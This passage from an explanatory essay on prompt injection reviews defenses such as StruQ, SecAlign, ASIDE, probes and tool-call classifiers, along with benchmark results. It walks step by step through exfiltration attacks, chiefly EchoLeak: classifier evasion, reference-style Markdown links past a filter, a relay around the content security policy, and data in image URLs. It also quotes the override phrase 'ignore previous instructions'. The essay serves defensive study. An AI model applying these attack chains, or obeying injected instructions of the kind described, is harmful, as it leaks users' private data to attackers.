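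Later evidence supports their caution. *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) describes a version that inserts a marker every eight characters into an email's sender, subject and body. It found that the method works mainly by breaking up the tokens of phrases that would otherwise trigger the model. If so, the marks disrupt certain wordings without creating anything like a data channel, and an attacker could look for wordings that still work. Wang and colleagues tested eight defenses and found that those working on the text alone gave no robust protection against more sophisticated attacks. The original test used one simple kind of attack, written without regard to the marking, so its low figures are weak evidence of how well the method would work against an attacker who knows the defense.

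### Training a model on two fields

StruQ, short for structured queries, combines marking with training. The developer's program passes the instruction and the data separately to a front end, which joins them with reserved tokens and deletes any copies of those tokens from the data. It repeats the deletion until none remain, because removing one copy can create another from the text on either side.

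The researchers then train the model on examples in this format. Some examples have a second instruction planted in the data, and the correct answer responds only to the instruction in the proper field. The planted instructions come from ordinary training examples, so nobody has to write attacks by hand.

Chen, Piet and colleagues tested StruQ on 208 tasks with an injected command to print "Hacked!". Handwritten attacks succeeded in at most 2 percent of cases, and the models' general usefulness barely changed. StruQ was much less effective against Greedy Coordinate Gradient (GCG), an attack that uses the model's parameters to search for extra tokens that make the attacker's output more likely. GCG succeeded in 58 percent of cases with a Llama model and 56 percent with a Mistral model, down from 97 and 99 percent without StruQ.

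Chen, Chaudhuri and colleagues (2024), in *SecAlign*, thought the training was at fault. StruQ rewards the right answer but never shows the model a wrong one. SecAlign gives it both:

```
StruQ:     loss = -log p(good | x)

SecAlign:  loss = -log σ( β log [p(good | x) / p0(good | x)]
                        - β log [p(bad | x)  / p0(bad | x)] )
```

Here x is a prompt with an injected instruction, "good" is the answer to the real instruction and "bad" is the answer to the injected one. The probability the model currently assigns to an answer is p, and p0 is the probability it assigned before this training. The function σ maps any number to the range from 0 to 1, and the constant β controls how strongly the comparison counts. Training adjusts the model to reduce the loss. With StruQ's formula, this only raises the probability of the good answer, while with SecAlign's it widens the gap between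 the probabilities of the good and bad answers.

The strongest attack the researchers tried succeeded in 1 percent of cases with a Mistral model and 8 percent with a Llama 3 model. With StruQ, the success rates on the same two models were 27 and 45 percent. The researchers took this as a hint that secure language models may be possible.

That hope depended on how strong the tested attacks were. Pandya and colleagues compared GCG with a version that chose its candidate tokens at random and found no significant difference, so SecAlign's resistance to GCG was weaker evidence of its security than it had seemed. Their own attack, which searches for tokens that draw the model's attention weights toward the injected instruction, succeeded against SecAlign in 75 percent of cases with Mistral and 57 percent with Llama 3. On a set of 40 examples with Llama 3, increasing the number of extra tokens from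 20 to 35 raised the success rate from 20 to 72.5 percent.

This attack requires the model's parameters and the full prompt, which Pandya and colleagues concede is often unrealistic. A company can keep the parameters from attackers by keeping its model private. But *Heads of Security* (2026) describes a later attack, RL-Hammer, that needs no such access and learns by trial and error. It succeeded nearly every time against a 70-billion-parameter Llama model trained with SecAlign. The training had made the model more likely to follow instructions in the right field, but a persistent attacker could still get around it.

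### Marking data inside the model

ASIDE comes closest to a separate channel because it marks data in the embeddings instead of the text. The surrounding software labels which tokens are data, and the model rotates their embeddings by 90 degrees, turning each successive pair of numbers (a, b) into (-b, a). The word "forward" then has one representation in an instruction and a different one in an email, from the first layer onward. Nothing a stranger writes in the email can undo the rotation. The researchers then fine-tune the model on ordinary examples, with no attacks among them, so that it learns to use the difference.

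Zverev and colleagues measured separation by placing an unrelated instruction in either the instruction field or the data field. A model scores well if it follows the instruction in the instruction field but ignores it in the data field. ASIDE raised the score by 12.3 to 44.1 percentage points, depending on the model. Averaged across models, the success rate of injected instructions fell from 14.7 to 4.9 percent on one benchmark of indirect attacks and from 45 to 36 percent on another. The gains were uneven, and one of the six models did slightly worse with ASIDE on the second benchmark.

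The researchers also checked that the rotation itself was responsible. When they gave the injected words the embeddings of instructions and changed nothing else, the model followed them almost twice as often. *Semantic Overlays* (2026) notes that ASIDE starts from models without instruction training, so the fairest comparison is with its own baseline. These figures all come from standard benchmarks and don't show how well ASIDE would resist attacks tuned to it.

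A probe could perfectly distinguish data from instructions at the first layer of a model with ASIDE, and an attacker could not forge the label, yet the model still followed many injected instructions. The redesigned telephone switch was safe because it no longer took commands from the voice line. But a model with ASIDE still processes both kinds of token with the same layers, and training only makes it less likely to follow instructions in the rotated data tokens. *Heads of Security* extends this approach by adjusting the attention weights according to how much the developer trusts each token.

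ASIDE also relies on the software to label the text correctly. This is easy for an email fetched through a tool, but harder when the user pastes a stranger's text into a request, because the software receives it all as the user's message. Zverev and colleagues tested only single exchanges with fixed roles and left longer conversations to future work.

### When the user wants the email obeyed

A bank's customers never need to write SQL, so the placeholder takes nothing away from them. But users of a mail assistant often want it to act on what other people have written. Suppose a colleague, Anna, emails a to-do list that includes booking a room and sending her the latest slides, and the user types "Please do what Anna asks." The instructions are in the email, so an assistant that perfectly separated instructions from data could list the tasks but not carry them out. The user would have to retype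 each one as a request.

Wang and colleagues call jobs like this context-dependent tasks. A coding agent may have to follow a project's configuration file, and an agent given a conditional request has to look something up before choosing an action. They built a benchmark, AgentPI, from five kinds of these tasks because earlier benchmarks mostly spelled out the whole job in the user's prompt. Many defenses had scored well on the earlier tests by suppressing what the agent read, and did poorly when the agent needed that material. Among the defenses that controlled the agent's actions, some refused complex tasks early, and some used up to three times the computation.

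An assistant can't tell from an instruction's wording alone whether to obey it. Hines and colleagues give the example of a request to transfer fifty dollars, which is harmless when it comes from the user but an attack when it comes from a document. Anna's request for the slides could appear word for word in a stranger's email. Hers is legitimate because the user chose to delegate to her, but the user may have done so vaguely. If her list also asks for the company's payroll file, the user's sentence technically covers it, though the user probably didn't mean it to.

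OpenAI advises users to give specific instructions and avoid prompts such as "review my emails and take whatever action is needed". This narrows what a stranger can plausibly ask for in an email, but the user loses some of the convenience that makes people want an agent. A developer can make a similar trade in software by having the user approve Anna's tasks one at a time, or by allowing the assistant to book rooms but not send files.

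Separating instructions from data also wouldn't stop false information, such as the planted notice about the rent account in the test by Fei and colleagues. An assistant that never follows instructions in emails can still pay the wrong account if such a notice is its only source for the account number. Preventing that payment requires tracking where the number came from, as information-flow control does.

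## Training and filtering models to resist injected instructions

No current model fully separates instructions from data, so developers try to make successful attacks rare. They train the model to resist instructions injected into an email, inspect the email before the model acts on it, and inspect the model's tool calls before ordinary software carries them out. In one set of tests from September 2026, attackers succeeded in about one attempt in a thousand against a newly released model that ran without filters for injected instructions. In another set, a stronger attacker succeeded against the same model in more than half of its attempts.

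### Why lists of forbidden phrases fail

The simplest filter blocks any incoming email that contains a phrase from a list, such as "ignore previous instructions". Howard's objection to lists of bad input applies more strongly here, because English has no special words that mark a command, whereas SQL has a small set of special characters. If an attacker's sentence has five parts, each with ten interchangeable wordings, the attacker can write it in 100,000 ways without changing its meaning. The attacker can also use another language or put the text in an image.

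Many successful attacks contain no such phrase. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) sorts the attacks from a public competition into 27 strategies. The strategy with the highest success rate, 4.3 percent, was to imitate the model's reasoning so that the attacker's command looked like the next step the model had already chosen. Other participants forged earlier messages from the user, or described the conversation as a simulation with its own control panel.

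A phrase list also blocks legitimate mail. A newsletter about prompt injection may quote a listed phrase, and a colleague may write "please ignore my previous instructions" after sending the wrong address. The list takes little effort to set up and will catch attacks copied without changes, but anyone who notices the block can reword the attack in seconds.

### Training a model to rank instructions by source

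StruQ and SecAlign train a model to obey one input field and treat the other as data. Real assistants take input from more than two sources, which deserve different amounts of trust. *The Instruction Hierarchy* (Wallace et al., OpenAI, 2024) proposes ranking the developer's instructions first, the user's second and anything in a tool result last.

In some training examples, the lower-ranked text is compatible with the higher-ranked text. For example, a developer has set up a mail assistant, the user asks for a summary in Spanish, and the correct answer is a summary in Spanish. In the rest, the two conflict. For example, an email tells the assistant to forward an invoice, and the correct answer is what the model would have written if the email had not contained that instruction. After training on many such examples, the model is more likely to summarize the email without forwarding the invoice.

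The model learns this ranking as a tendency, so text that sounds like the user can make the model more likely to treat it as the user's, a weakness Ye and colleagues found in role markers. The ranking also doesn't determine how much the user meant to delegate with a request such as "Please do what Anna asks."

### Training on attacks that worked

In adversarial training, the developer looks for attacks that beat the current model, adds them to the training examples along with the correct responses, trains the model again and repeats the search. The ideal version solves this problem:

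```
minimize over θ:   average over tasks x of [ maximum over attacks a of L(θ, x, a) ]
```

Here θ stands for the model's parameters, x for a task such as summarizing the inbox, and a for the text the attacker adds. The loss L is high when the model follows the attack. The inner maximum is the worst attack anyone could write for that task. There are too many possible texts to compute it, so developers use the worst attacks they have found. The trained model then resists those attacks and similar ones. How well it resists unfamiliar attacks depends on how widely the developers searched.

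Developers use both people and software to search for attacks that work. Dziemian and colleagues gave each participating company the attacks that had worked on its own models, and gave the full set to government institutes in Britain and the United States. In December 2025, OpenAI described how it uses a language model, trained by trial and error, to find attacks that work on its Atlas browser agent, and then trains new versions of the agent to resist them.

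The competition also gives some indirect evidence that training matters. Gemini 2.5 Pro and Kimi K2 both scored about 85 percent on GPQA Diamond, a test of difficult science questions, but attackers succeeded in 8.5 percent of attempts on Gemini and 4.8 percent on Kimi. Across all the models, the correlation between this score and the attack success rate was -0.31, too weak to distinguish from chance in a group this small. Dziemian and colleagues conclude that robustness depends more on a model's family and training than on its general ability. Companies differ in many other ways, so the comparison can't isolate the effect of training, but it gives developers little reason to expect that a more capable model will resist injection without specific work on the problem.

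### Probes and tool-call classifiers

A developer can also inspect the model's inputs without changing the model. The *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5, Anthropic's report on the model's tests, risks and safeguards, describes the "prompt injection probes" that Anthropic uses in many of its products. The probes inspect each tool result before the model acts on it and flag content that looks like an injected instruction. A probe that reads the model's internal activity, like the one Ye and colleagues trained, can respond to what a sentence means, so rewording an attack is less likely to evade it than to evade a filter that looks for listed phrases.

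Another classifier can inspect the model's output. If the user asked the mail assistant for a summary and the model issues a tool call to send an invoice to an unknown address, the classifier can block the call even if the injected instruction went undetected. Anthropic combines such a classifier with the probes in a setting called auto mode, which had become the default in Claude Code by September 2026.

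Anthropic argues that an attack has to defeat both layers independently. If each layer missed one attack in ten and the misses were unrelated, only one attack in a hundred would get through. But an attacker can choose actions that both layers would treat as routine. In one of the competition's scenarios, a fake marketing email had to make an assistant mark a message about a contract deadline as read and leave it out of the summary. Mail assistants routinely mark messages as read, so a classifier for dangerous tool calls has little to detect. Both layers would tend to miss the same attacks of this kind, so more than one in a hundred would get through.

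Filters must also avoid flagging ordinary text, which is hard because hostile text is so rare. Khodayari and colleagues confirmed planted instructions on about eight pages per million web addresses. If a filter caught all eight and wrongly flagged 1 percent of the rest, it would raise about 10,000 false alarms. Even if there were ten times as many hostile pages, fewer than one alarm in a hundred would be real. A developer who responds by making the filter less sensitive makes it easier for attackers to evade, and readers can't see that tradeoff when a success rate is published without a false-alarm rate.

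### Why fixed test sets mislead

By 2025, many researchers had published defenses with attack success rates near zero. They had usually measured those rates using a fixed list of known attacks or a weak automatic search for new ones. Nasr and colleagues' *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025) tested defenses against adaptive attacks, which the attacker revises according to how the defense behaves.

Researchers tested 12 published defenses against prompt injection and against jailbreaks, which are attempts to make a model break its safety rules. The defenses included spotlighting, StruQ, a later version of SecAlign and several filters that scan text for injections. For each defense, the researchers tuned a general search method to attack it. Some searches used the model's parameters to find better wording, some trained an attacking model by trial and error, and some had a language model propose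 variations and kept the best. People also attacked the defenses by hand in a prize competition. The attacks succeeded more than 90 percent of the time against most of the 12, although the developers of most of these defenses had reported rates close to zero.

The original figures may have been accurate for the attacks tested. But a fixed list contains attacks that worked on earlier systems, and a new defense can stop them all by blocking features they happen to share, which the next attacker then avoids.

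Nasr and colleagues gave their attackers time, computing power and knowledge of the defense. The 90 percent success rate under those conditions shows that the earlier near-zero rates were little or no evidence of how often a determined attacker would succeed. A stranger's first email may succeed less often than 90 percent of the time.

### A public competition

The security firm Gray Swan ran the competition that Dziemian and colleagues describe. Britain's AI Security Institute, its American counterpart and several AI companies supported it, and some of those companies' employees co-wrote the paper. Over three weeks, 464 people made about 272,000 attack attempts on 13 models for a share of $40,000. Participants could not see the models' names, which made it harder for them to favor or avoid a particular company.

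In 18 of the 41 scenarios the agent used ordinary tools such as email or shopping, in 15 it worked on code, and in 8 it operated a computer through its screen, mouse and keyboard. Each participant could fill in one piece of text that an outsider might plausibly control, such as the body of an email or a comment in a code repository. The goal was to make the agent carry out a specified harmful action while giving the user no sign of it in its final reply. Software checked whether the agent had carried out the action, and in most scenarios an automated judge also scored the reply.

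Participants made 8,648 successful attempts, including some against every model. The success rate per attempt ranged from 0.5 percent for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5 percent for Gemini 2.5 Pro. Opus 4.5 failed at least once in 13 of the 37 scenarios in the main rounds, and Gemini 2.5 Pro failed at least once in all 37. Successes accumulated at a roughly constant rate, so there was no sign that participants were running out of attacks.

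These rates overstate the danger in one respect, because participants could read the whole conversation and knew the exact action they had to cause, which a stranger sending an email would have to guess. They also understate it, because an attack usually counted as a failure if the final reply revealed it, even when the harm, such as sending an invoice to a stranger, had already been done. Gemini 2.5 Pro took the harmful action in about 16 percent of attempts, nearly twice its headline rate. Opus 4.5 and GPT-5 did so in 1 to 3 percent.

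The researchers then took attacks that had worked on one model and tried them on the others. The 44 attacks that had succeeded against Opus 4.5 worked between 44 and 81 percent of the time on every other model. None of the attacks that had succeeded against Qwen3 VL, one of the weakest models, worked on Opus 4.5. A test set made mostly of attacks on weak models will therefore make a strong model look more resistant than it is. One template, which told the model it was inside a simulation, worked with small changes in 21 scenarios and on nine models, so an attacker doesn't always need a new idea for each target.

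### The 2026 measurements

Gray Swan has kept running competitions and turns the results into a benchmark. The version in the Opus 5 system card, from July 2026, has 28 scenarios and 1,130 attacks, chosen because they worked on several models. Anthropic reports the chance that an attacker succeeds in one attempt and within 15. For Opus 5 these were 0.2 and 2.0 percent, down from 0.5 and 5.5 percent for Opus 4.8. For GPT-5.6 Sol, the most capable version of OpenAI's GPT-5.6, they were 3.1 and 20.0 percent. For OpenAI's smaller GPT-5.6 models, the chance within 15 attempts was 30.4 percent for Terra and 43.9 percent for Luna. The lowest chance within 15 attempts for a model from a company other than Anthropic was 16.5 percent, for Meta's Muse Spark.

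Anthropic published this comparison about its own product, but the setup did not obviously favor Anthropic. Its models ran without extra safeguards against injection, while the others ran in their public versions, possibly with such safeguards. A larger concern is that the benchmark is a fixed list of 1,130 attacks, which nobody revised after seeing how Opus 5 responded.

The list of attacks changed within weeks. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1, dated September 1, uses a newer version with 37 scenarios and 1,804 attacks. The success rate of attacks on Opus 5 within 15 attempts rose from 2.0 to 4.8 percent. The new attacks probably explain much of this, though the test conditions also changed. Fable 5.1 did better, at 0.1 percent for one attempt and 1.0 percent within 15. The strongest model from another company, Gemini 3.7 Flash, was at 9.2 percent, and most others were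 between 24 and 53 percent.

Anthropic also uses Shade, an automated attacker from Gray Swan that improves by trial and error. Gray Swan trains Shade on the test scenarios against earlier Claude models, then runs it against new models with 200 attempts at each scenario. For the browser test, Anthropic instead collected attacks that worked on an older model, Opus 4.7, and tested each newer model with ten attempts at each of 110 scenarios.

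| Test of Fable 5.1 | Success without injection safeguards | Success with injection safeguards |
|---|---|---|
| Coding, earlier version of Shade | 9.26% of attempts; 31 of 40 scenarios | 2.05% of attempts; 18 of 40 scenarios (probes) |
| Coding, stronger version of Shade | 56.87% of attempts; 38 of 40 scenarios | 12.80% of attempts; 36 of 40 scenarios (probes) |
| Operating a screen, Shade | 0.07% of attempts; 2 of 14 scenarios | 0.07% of attempts; 2 of 14 scenarios (probes) |
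| Browser, attacks found on Opus 4.7 | 2.64% of attempts; 10 of 110 scenarios | 0% of attempts; 0 of 110 scenarios (auto mode) |

The two coding rows use the same 40 scenarios. Gray Swan trained the stronger version of Shade for longer and on more varied attacks, and its success rate was six times higher. Against Opus 5, the stronger version succeeded in 90.93 percent of attempts. Probes cut that to 18.21 percent, but Shade still found at least one successful attack in each of the 40 scenarios, so the probes only delayed an attacker who needs one success.

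Anthropic calls this test highly permissive, which is fair because Shade trained on the same scenarios used in the test, while a real attacker usually doesn't know what the victim's agent is working on. The company still plans to make it the main coding test. It comes closer than the other measurements to what Nasr and colleagues asked for, although Shade trained against earlier models and didn't adjust to the newest ones.

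The kind of work most vulnerable to attack also varies from test to test. In the competition, agents using ordinary tools were the easiest to attack. On the September benchmark, no attack succeeded when Fable 5.1 used ordinary tools, and it was weakest when operating a screen, where attacks succeeded 4.1 percent of the time within 15 attempts. With Shade, attacks succeeded far more often in coding than in operating a screen. VentureBeat reported the reverse for Opus 4.6 in February 2026. No attack succeeded in 200 attempts in a coding test, but when the model operated a screen, the success rate was 17.8 percent on the first attempt and 78.6 percent by the 200th. A developer therefore can't safely use a figure measured on one kind of feature to estimate the risk of another.

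### When one safeguard weakens another

Fable 5.1's high attack success rates in coding come from requests that an older model, Opus 4.8, answered in its place. Anthropic runs a separate classifier that detects suspected requests for hacking help, and the product sends those to Opus 4.8. In the test with the stronger version of Shade, this happened to about 64 percent of requests. No attack succeeded in the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself.

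Zero successful attacks is an encouraging result, but the hacking classifier had already removed the requests it flagged as suspicious, so the remaining attacks may have been weaker. Some attacks succeeded directly against Opus 5 and the earlier Fable 5.

The fallback also affected comparisons over time. In July, the earlier version of Shade succeeded against Opus 5 in 0.56 percent of coding attempts. In September, Anthropic reported 2.68 percent for the same model, but this figure included the fallback, which had handled 57 percent of the requests. The September figure is closer to what a customer would experience. Anthropic says it is working on how the classifiers interact. Until this is resolved, a safeguard meant to keep a model from helping hackers can leave a coding agent more exposed to them. A developer who chooses a model for its resistance to injection may find that a different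 model handles the requests where that resistance matters most.

These figures also age quickly. Anthropic replaced Fable 5.1 after ten weeks, according to Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026).

### From one attempt to many

If every attempt had the same chance p of success and the attempts were independent, the chance of at least one success in k attempts would be:

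```
P(at least one success) = 1 - (1 - p)^k
```

The term (1 - p)^k is the chance that all k attempts fail, so the chance that at least one succeeds is 1 - (1 - p)^k. For Opus 5 on the July benchmark, p is 0.2 percent and k is 15, so the formula gives 3.0 percent, while Anthropic measured 2.0 percent. Rounding could explain most of this gap, because a true rate of 0.15 percent would also be reported as 0.2 percent and would give 2.2 percent. Rounding can't explain the gap for GPT-5.6 Sol, where the formula gives 38 percent and the measured figure was 20 percent.

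The gap between the formula and the measured rates widens as the number of attempts grows. According to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, strong attacks on Opus 4.5 in an earlier Gray Swan benchmark succeeded 4.7 percent of the time on one attempt, 33.6 percent within 10 attempts and 63 percent within 100. The formula, which assumes that attempts are independent, gives 38 percent for 10 attempts and 99 percent for 100.

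So the attempts are not independent draws with a single success rate. Some scenarios are much easier to attack than others, and an average hides this. Suppose that 6 percent of attacks succeed in one scenario out of 30, and none succeed in the other 29. The average success rate over all scenarios is then 0.2 percent for one attempt. Within 15 attempts, the weak scenario fails about 60 percent of the time, which makes the average 2.0 percent. These averages match Opus 5's figures, but other mixtures would too, so Opus 5 may not have exactly this pattern. Still, a model with a low average can have a few tasks on which a patient attacker will probably succeed, and a developer would want to know whether the product's main task is one of them.

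A score of zero needs similar care. In July, Opus 5 with auto mode resisted every attack in 129 browser scenarios. Without safeguards, 3.70 percent of attempts had succeeded, compared with 31.5 percent for Opus 4.8. To find how high the true failure rate could be, one can look for the rate at which 129 clean results in a row would happen only 5 percent of the time:

```
(1 - p)^129 = 0.05,   so   p = 1 - 0.05^(1/129) ≈ 0.023
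```

The result is compatible with attacks succeeding in up to about 2.3 percent of scenarios, at 95 percent confidence. For the 110 scenarios in September, the limit is 2.7 percent. Each scenario had ten attempts, but attempts at one scenario tend to succeed or fail together, so treating all 1,290 as independent would make the limit ten times too low. The 2.3 percent limit also assumes that the scenarios are a random sample of what users will meet, but Anthropic selected them. In September it used attacks found on an older model, so the limit doesn't cover an attacker who practises against auto mode itself.

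Even a small success rate can also produce many victims. If a million assistants each read one hostile email and 0.1 percent follow it, the attacker hijacks 1,000 of them. That rate is an average over many different attacks, and most attackers would get nothing, but one who found a working email would do far better by sending it to everyone. When Dziemian and colleagues repeated successful attacks on the same Claude and GPT models, at least half worked again. Real inboxes differ more than repeated runs of one scenario, so the share would probably be lower, but it could still be hundreds of times higher than the average rate.

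### Whether the problem is nearly solved

Some people see the July results as close to a solution. The Decoder titled its article *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. Boris Cherny, who created Claude Code at Anthropic, wrote that with trained resistance, probes and auto mode together, the attack success rate "drops to ~0", as quoted in ClawSouls' *The most exciting line was buried in a system card*.

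There is a good case that this describes ordinary risk. Most of the planted text that Khodayari and colleagues found on the web was crude, and Google saw little use of advanced techniques. A feature built on Opus 5 with auto mode may go a long time without a serious hijack if it faces only attacks like these. The improvement since Opus 4.8 is also too large to be noise.

Simon Willison, the programmer who named prompt injection, wrote in 2025 that catching 95 percent of attacks is a failing grade in web security, because an attacker keeps trying until one gets through. The newest systems stop well over 95 percent of attacks on most tests, but his argument applies to any attack success rate above zero that an attacker can find a way to raise, and the stronger version of Shade raised it a great deal. Schneier's comparison with the telephone network, where only a redesign ended the attacks,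 supports the same caution. A reader commenting on Schneier on Security's *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026) wrote that people will always find vulnerabilities and exploit them.

The two sides disagree mainly about which attacker to plan for. Anthropic argues that real attackers can't do what Shade does, because they don't know the victim's setup and repeated attempts raise the chance of detection. This is convincing for an agent inside one company's private systems, but less so for a mail assistant that anyone can subscribe to. An attacker can open an account, fill the inbox with plausible messages, test thousands of emails on it, and send the victim only the one that worked.

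## Checking what the model produces before anything acts on it

An email that gets past the model's training and every filter still does nothing until other software acts on the model's reply. A developer can check the reply before a browser displays it, a database runs it as a query, or a mail server sends it.

The model's reply needs checking because anyone who influences what the model reads can influence what it writes. Goedecke writes in *Principles for coding securely with LLMs* that "you must treat LLM output like user input." The balance page, which had to treat a name from a web form as hostile, should treat a name from a model the same way if the model has read a stranger's email, even if the model has given correct answers for months. OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* covers the failure to do this and compares it to giving users indirect access to whatever the output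 reaches.

The old fixes work fully here because databases and browsers do separate commands from data, as Respan (2026), a vendor of testing tools, points out. A parameterized query gives the same guarantee whether a person or a model supplied the value, so the developer doesn't need to know whether an attacker misled the model.

In August 2026 OWASP moved improper output handling from fifth to tenth place on its list of risks in language model applications. Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026) attributes the drop to the greater urgency of other risks. Practitioners' votes count for three-quarters of the ranking and recorded incidents for one-quarter, so the new position is weak evidence that the flaw has become rarer. OWASP also widened the entry to cover command-line terminals and software that automatically loads images.

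### Text on a screen

If a web page inserts a model's reply directly into its HTML, the browser will run any script in the reply. This is cross-site scripting with the model as the courier. The basic fix is encoding, which replaces each character that has a special meaning in HTML with a code for displaying it:

```
<b>Total</b>    becomes    &lt;b&gt;Total&lt;/b&gt;
```

Escaping the model's reply makes the browser show angle brackets as text instead of treating them as the start of a tag. This works for any reply, but it also removes legitimate formatting. Most AI features use headings and lists, so they have the model write Markdown, a simple notation that software converts to HTML. A sanitizer then parses the HTML and keeps only elements on a short permitted list, such as paragraphs, lists and bold text. The sanitizer has to run after the conversion because the conversion can create tags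 that were not in the Markdown.

Encoding must also suit the destination. Coding agents often print to a terminal, where certain control characters move the cursor, change colors or hide text. Embrace The Red's *Terminal DiLLMa* describes how a model's output can include these characters and so control the terminal. Trail of Bits' *Deceiving users with ANSI terminal codes in MCP* (2025) found that version 0.2.76 of Claude Code did not filter them from tool descriptions or tool outputs, so a hostile tool could hide instructions from the user that the model would still read. HTML encoding wouldn't help, because it doesn't change control characters. The software has to remove them or print them as visible symbols.

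### Links and images that carry data out

A web address can carry data as well as a location. When a browser requests `https://example.com/logo.png?id=4711`, the server at example.com receives 4711 and can log it. If a misled model puts an invoice total in the address instead, the server's owner learns the total. A link sends the data only when the user clicks it, but a browser normally loads an image as soon as it appears. A reply containing such an image needs no script, so a sanitizer that permits images will let it through.

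*Trust No AI* (2024) describes an early case in which a phishing email could make Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant for office software, search the user's inbox and put what it found into a link as invisible characters. A researcher found the flaw in February 2024, and Microsoft fixed it in July. Amazon dealt with a similar flaw in its assistant Amazon Q by no longer displaying any links.

Developers can keep links but restrict where they lead. The software parses the reply, compares the server in each address with a list of permitted servers, and removes any other address or shows it as plain text. For images, the safest choice is not to load them automatically. Developers can also send the browser a content security policy, which lists the servers from which the page may load images, scripts and other material. The browser enforces this list even if the address check misses something.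 Many products display a reply while the model is still writing it, so the address check has to run before each new piece appears.

Removing the part of the address after the question mark isn't enough, because the data can go elsewhere in the address, and even a choice among fixed addresses conveys information. If an attacker's server hosts 1,024 images, each request for one of them reveals log2(1,024) = 10 bits. A 16-digit number contains about 53 bits, so six requests in a known order could reveal it. The check has to restrict the destination, because the developer can't list every way to encode a secret.

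### EchoLeak

In January 2025, researchers at Aim Labs, part of Aim Security, reported a chain of flaws in Microsoft 365 Copilot that defeated both kinds of check. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) is the finders' account of the attack, now catalogued as CVE-2025-32711. The attacker sent one email, and the attack ran when the victim later asked Copilot a question. The victim didn't have to open the email or click anything.

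The email first had to pass a Microsoft classifier that looks for injected instructions. It passed because its instructions were addressed to the human recipient and never mentioned AI or Copilot. Taken alone, the email looked like a request to a colleague.

Copilot also had to retrieve the email. It answers questions by searching the user's mailbox, files and Teams chats for relevant material, and an email about one subject would match few questions. The researchers therefore wrote a long email with many sections, each presented as a guide to a common workplace subject such as onboarding or leave. In their test, Copilot loaded the email into its context window when asked about various subjects.

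The instructions then had the model pick the most sensitive information in its context and put it in a web address. That information could come from the chat history or from anything Copilot had fetched for the user. Ravia compares the email to an unprivileged program that uses a privileged one to reach protected resources, as happened with Hardy's compiler.

Copilot removed external links from replies, but the filter recognized only one of the ways to write a link in Markdown. Both of these produce the same link:

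```
[report](https://example.com/report)

[report][1]
[1]: https://example.com/report
```

The filter caught the first form but missed the second. Images have the same two forms, so the researchers could also use the second form to get an image into the reply. A filter that parsed the Markdown exactly as the display software did would have found the same address in both forms.

The last obstacle was the browser's content security policy, which blocked images from the attacker's server but allowed them from many Microsoft domains. The researchers first found a SharePoint service that would fetch an outside address, but the victim had to accept an invitation to the attacker's site. They then found a Teams service that needed no invitation. Because the policy checked only the first server, the browser could request the image from Teams, and Teams, itself a confused deputy, passed the request,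 with the secret in it, to the attacker's server.

The email also kept Copilot from citing it as a source. According to *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), a case study based on public accounts, the user would have seen nothing more suspicious than a broken link or image.

Microsoft deployed a fix on its own servers in May 2025 and published an advisory on June 11. The company said that customers didn't need to do anything and that it had no evidence of real attacks. Accounts are less definite about which step of the attack the fix blocked. Reddy and Gujral write that Copilot now strips the overlooked kind of link, along with embedded images, from incoming external content, and that Microsoft reportedly added options to keep external messages out of Copilot's context. They don't report whether the fix closed the Teams relay. Stripping links from an email removes an address the model could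 copy, but a model can also compose an address from a description, so Copilot would still need a reliable check on its replies.

Microsoft rated the severity of CVE-2025-32711 at 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5, according to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026). Intruder's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025) records that Microsoft classed the flaw as CWE-74, the general category for injection into a downstream component. The category fits because the last steps of the attack relied on ordinary web software.

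In a chart of defenses against such an attack, Reddy and Gujral predict that a list of permitted addresses and a strict content security policy would stop the automatic leak, but that labeling external text or limiting Copilot to internal sources would not. They ran no experiments to test these predictions. The prediction about the content security policy depends heavily on how strict it is, since Copilot already had one with a list of permitted servers. A list protects data only if none of the servers on it will forward a request to a server the attacker chooses.

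### The same leak in later products

In a note on Ravia's article under the same title, Willison called EchoLeak an extended variant of a leak already seen in a dozen products. Underhill (2026), in *SearchLeak Flaw Exposed Sensitive Data in Microsoft 365 Copilot*, reported in June that another flaw could have exposed Copilot data after one click. On December 3, 2026, the researchers who found EchoLeak, now at Cato Networks, disclosed three more attacks on Copilot, which they call ReLeak and which need no click. Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, quotes their verdict that "too little progress has been made."

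Each ReLeak attack starts with an unread email. AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) reports that data can then leave through an image address, a link to a saved file, or code. The code route worked even though Microsoft's documentation said that the environment running the code blocked outgoing traffic. Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026) reports that the image route sent data to the attacker's server through Bing. Bing was already on the list of permitted image servers that Ravia published in 2025, which suggests that Microsoft had dealt with the Teams route without removing every server that could be used the same way. Microsoft patched the three flaws between September 17 and November 15, and Cato knows of no real attacks that used them.

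A browser policy can't block a request that the browser doesn't make. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* describes ShadowLeak, an attack on ChatGPT's Deep Research agent. Hidden instructions in an email made the agent collect data from the user's Gmail account and visit a web address that contained the data. The request came from the provider's servers, so the user's browser and the employer's monitoring software might not have detected it. OpenAI fixed the flaw in August 2025. In a product like this, the check on destinations has to run on the server that fetches pages for the agent.

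### Queries that a model writes

Some products let people query a database in plain language. Tanner (2025), in *Understanding and Protecting Against LLM05*, imagines a business platform where an analyst types a question, a model turns it into SQL, and the software runs the query. OWASP recommends parameterized queries for every database operation that involves model output, but these protect a query only if the developer has fixed its structure. If the model writes the whole query, its output determines the structure as well as the values, and the database will run any valid command its permissions allow.

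The developer can restore the separation by writing the queries in advance. The model then only chooses one and supplies some of the values. A question about spending in March could use this template:

```
SELECT category, SUM(amount)
FROM payments
WHERE customer_id = ? AND month = ?
GROUP BY category
```

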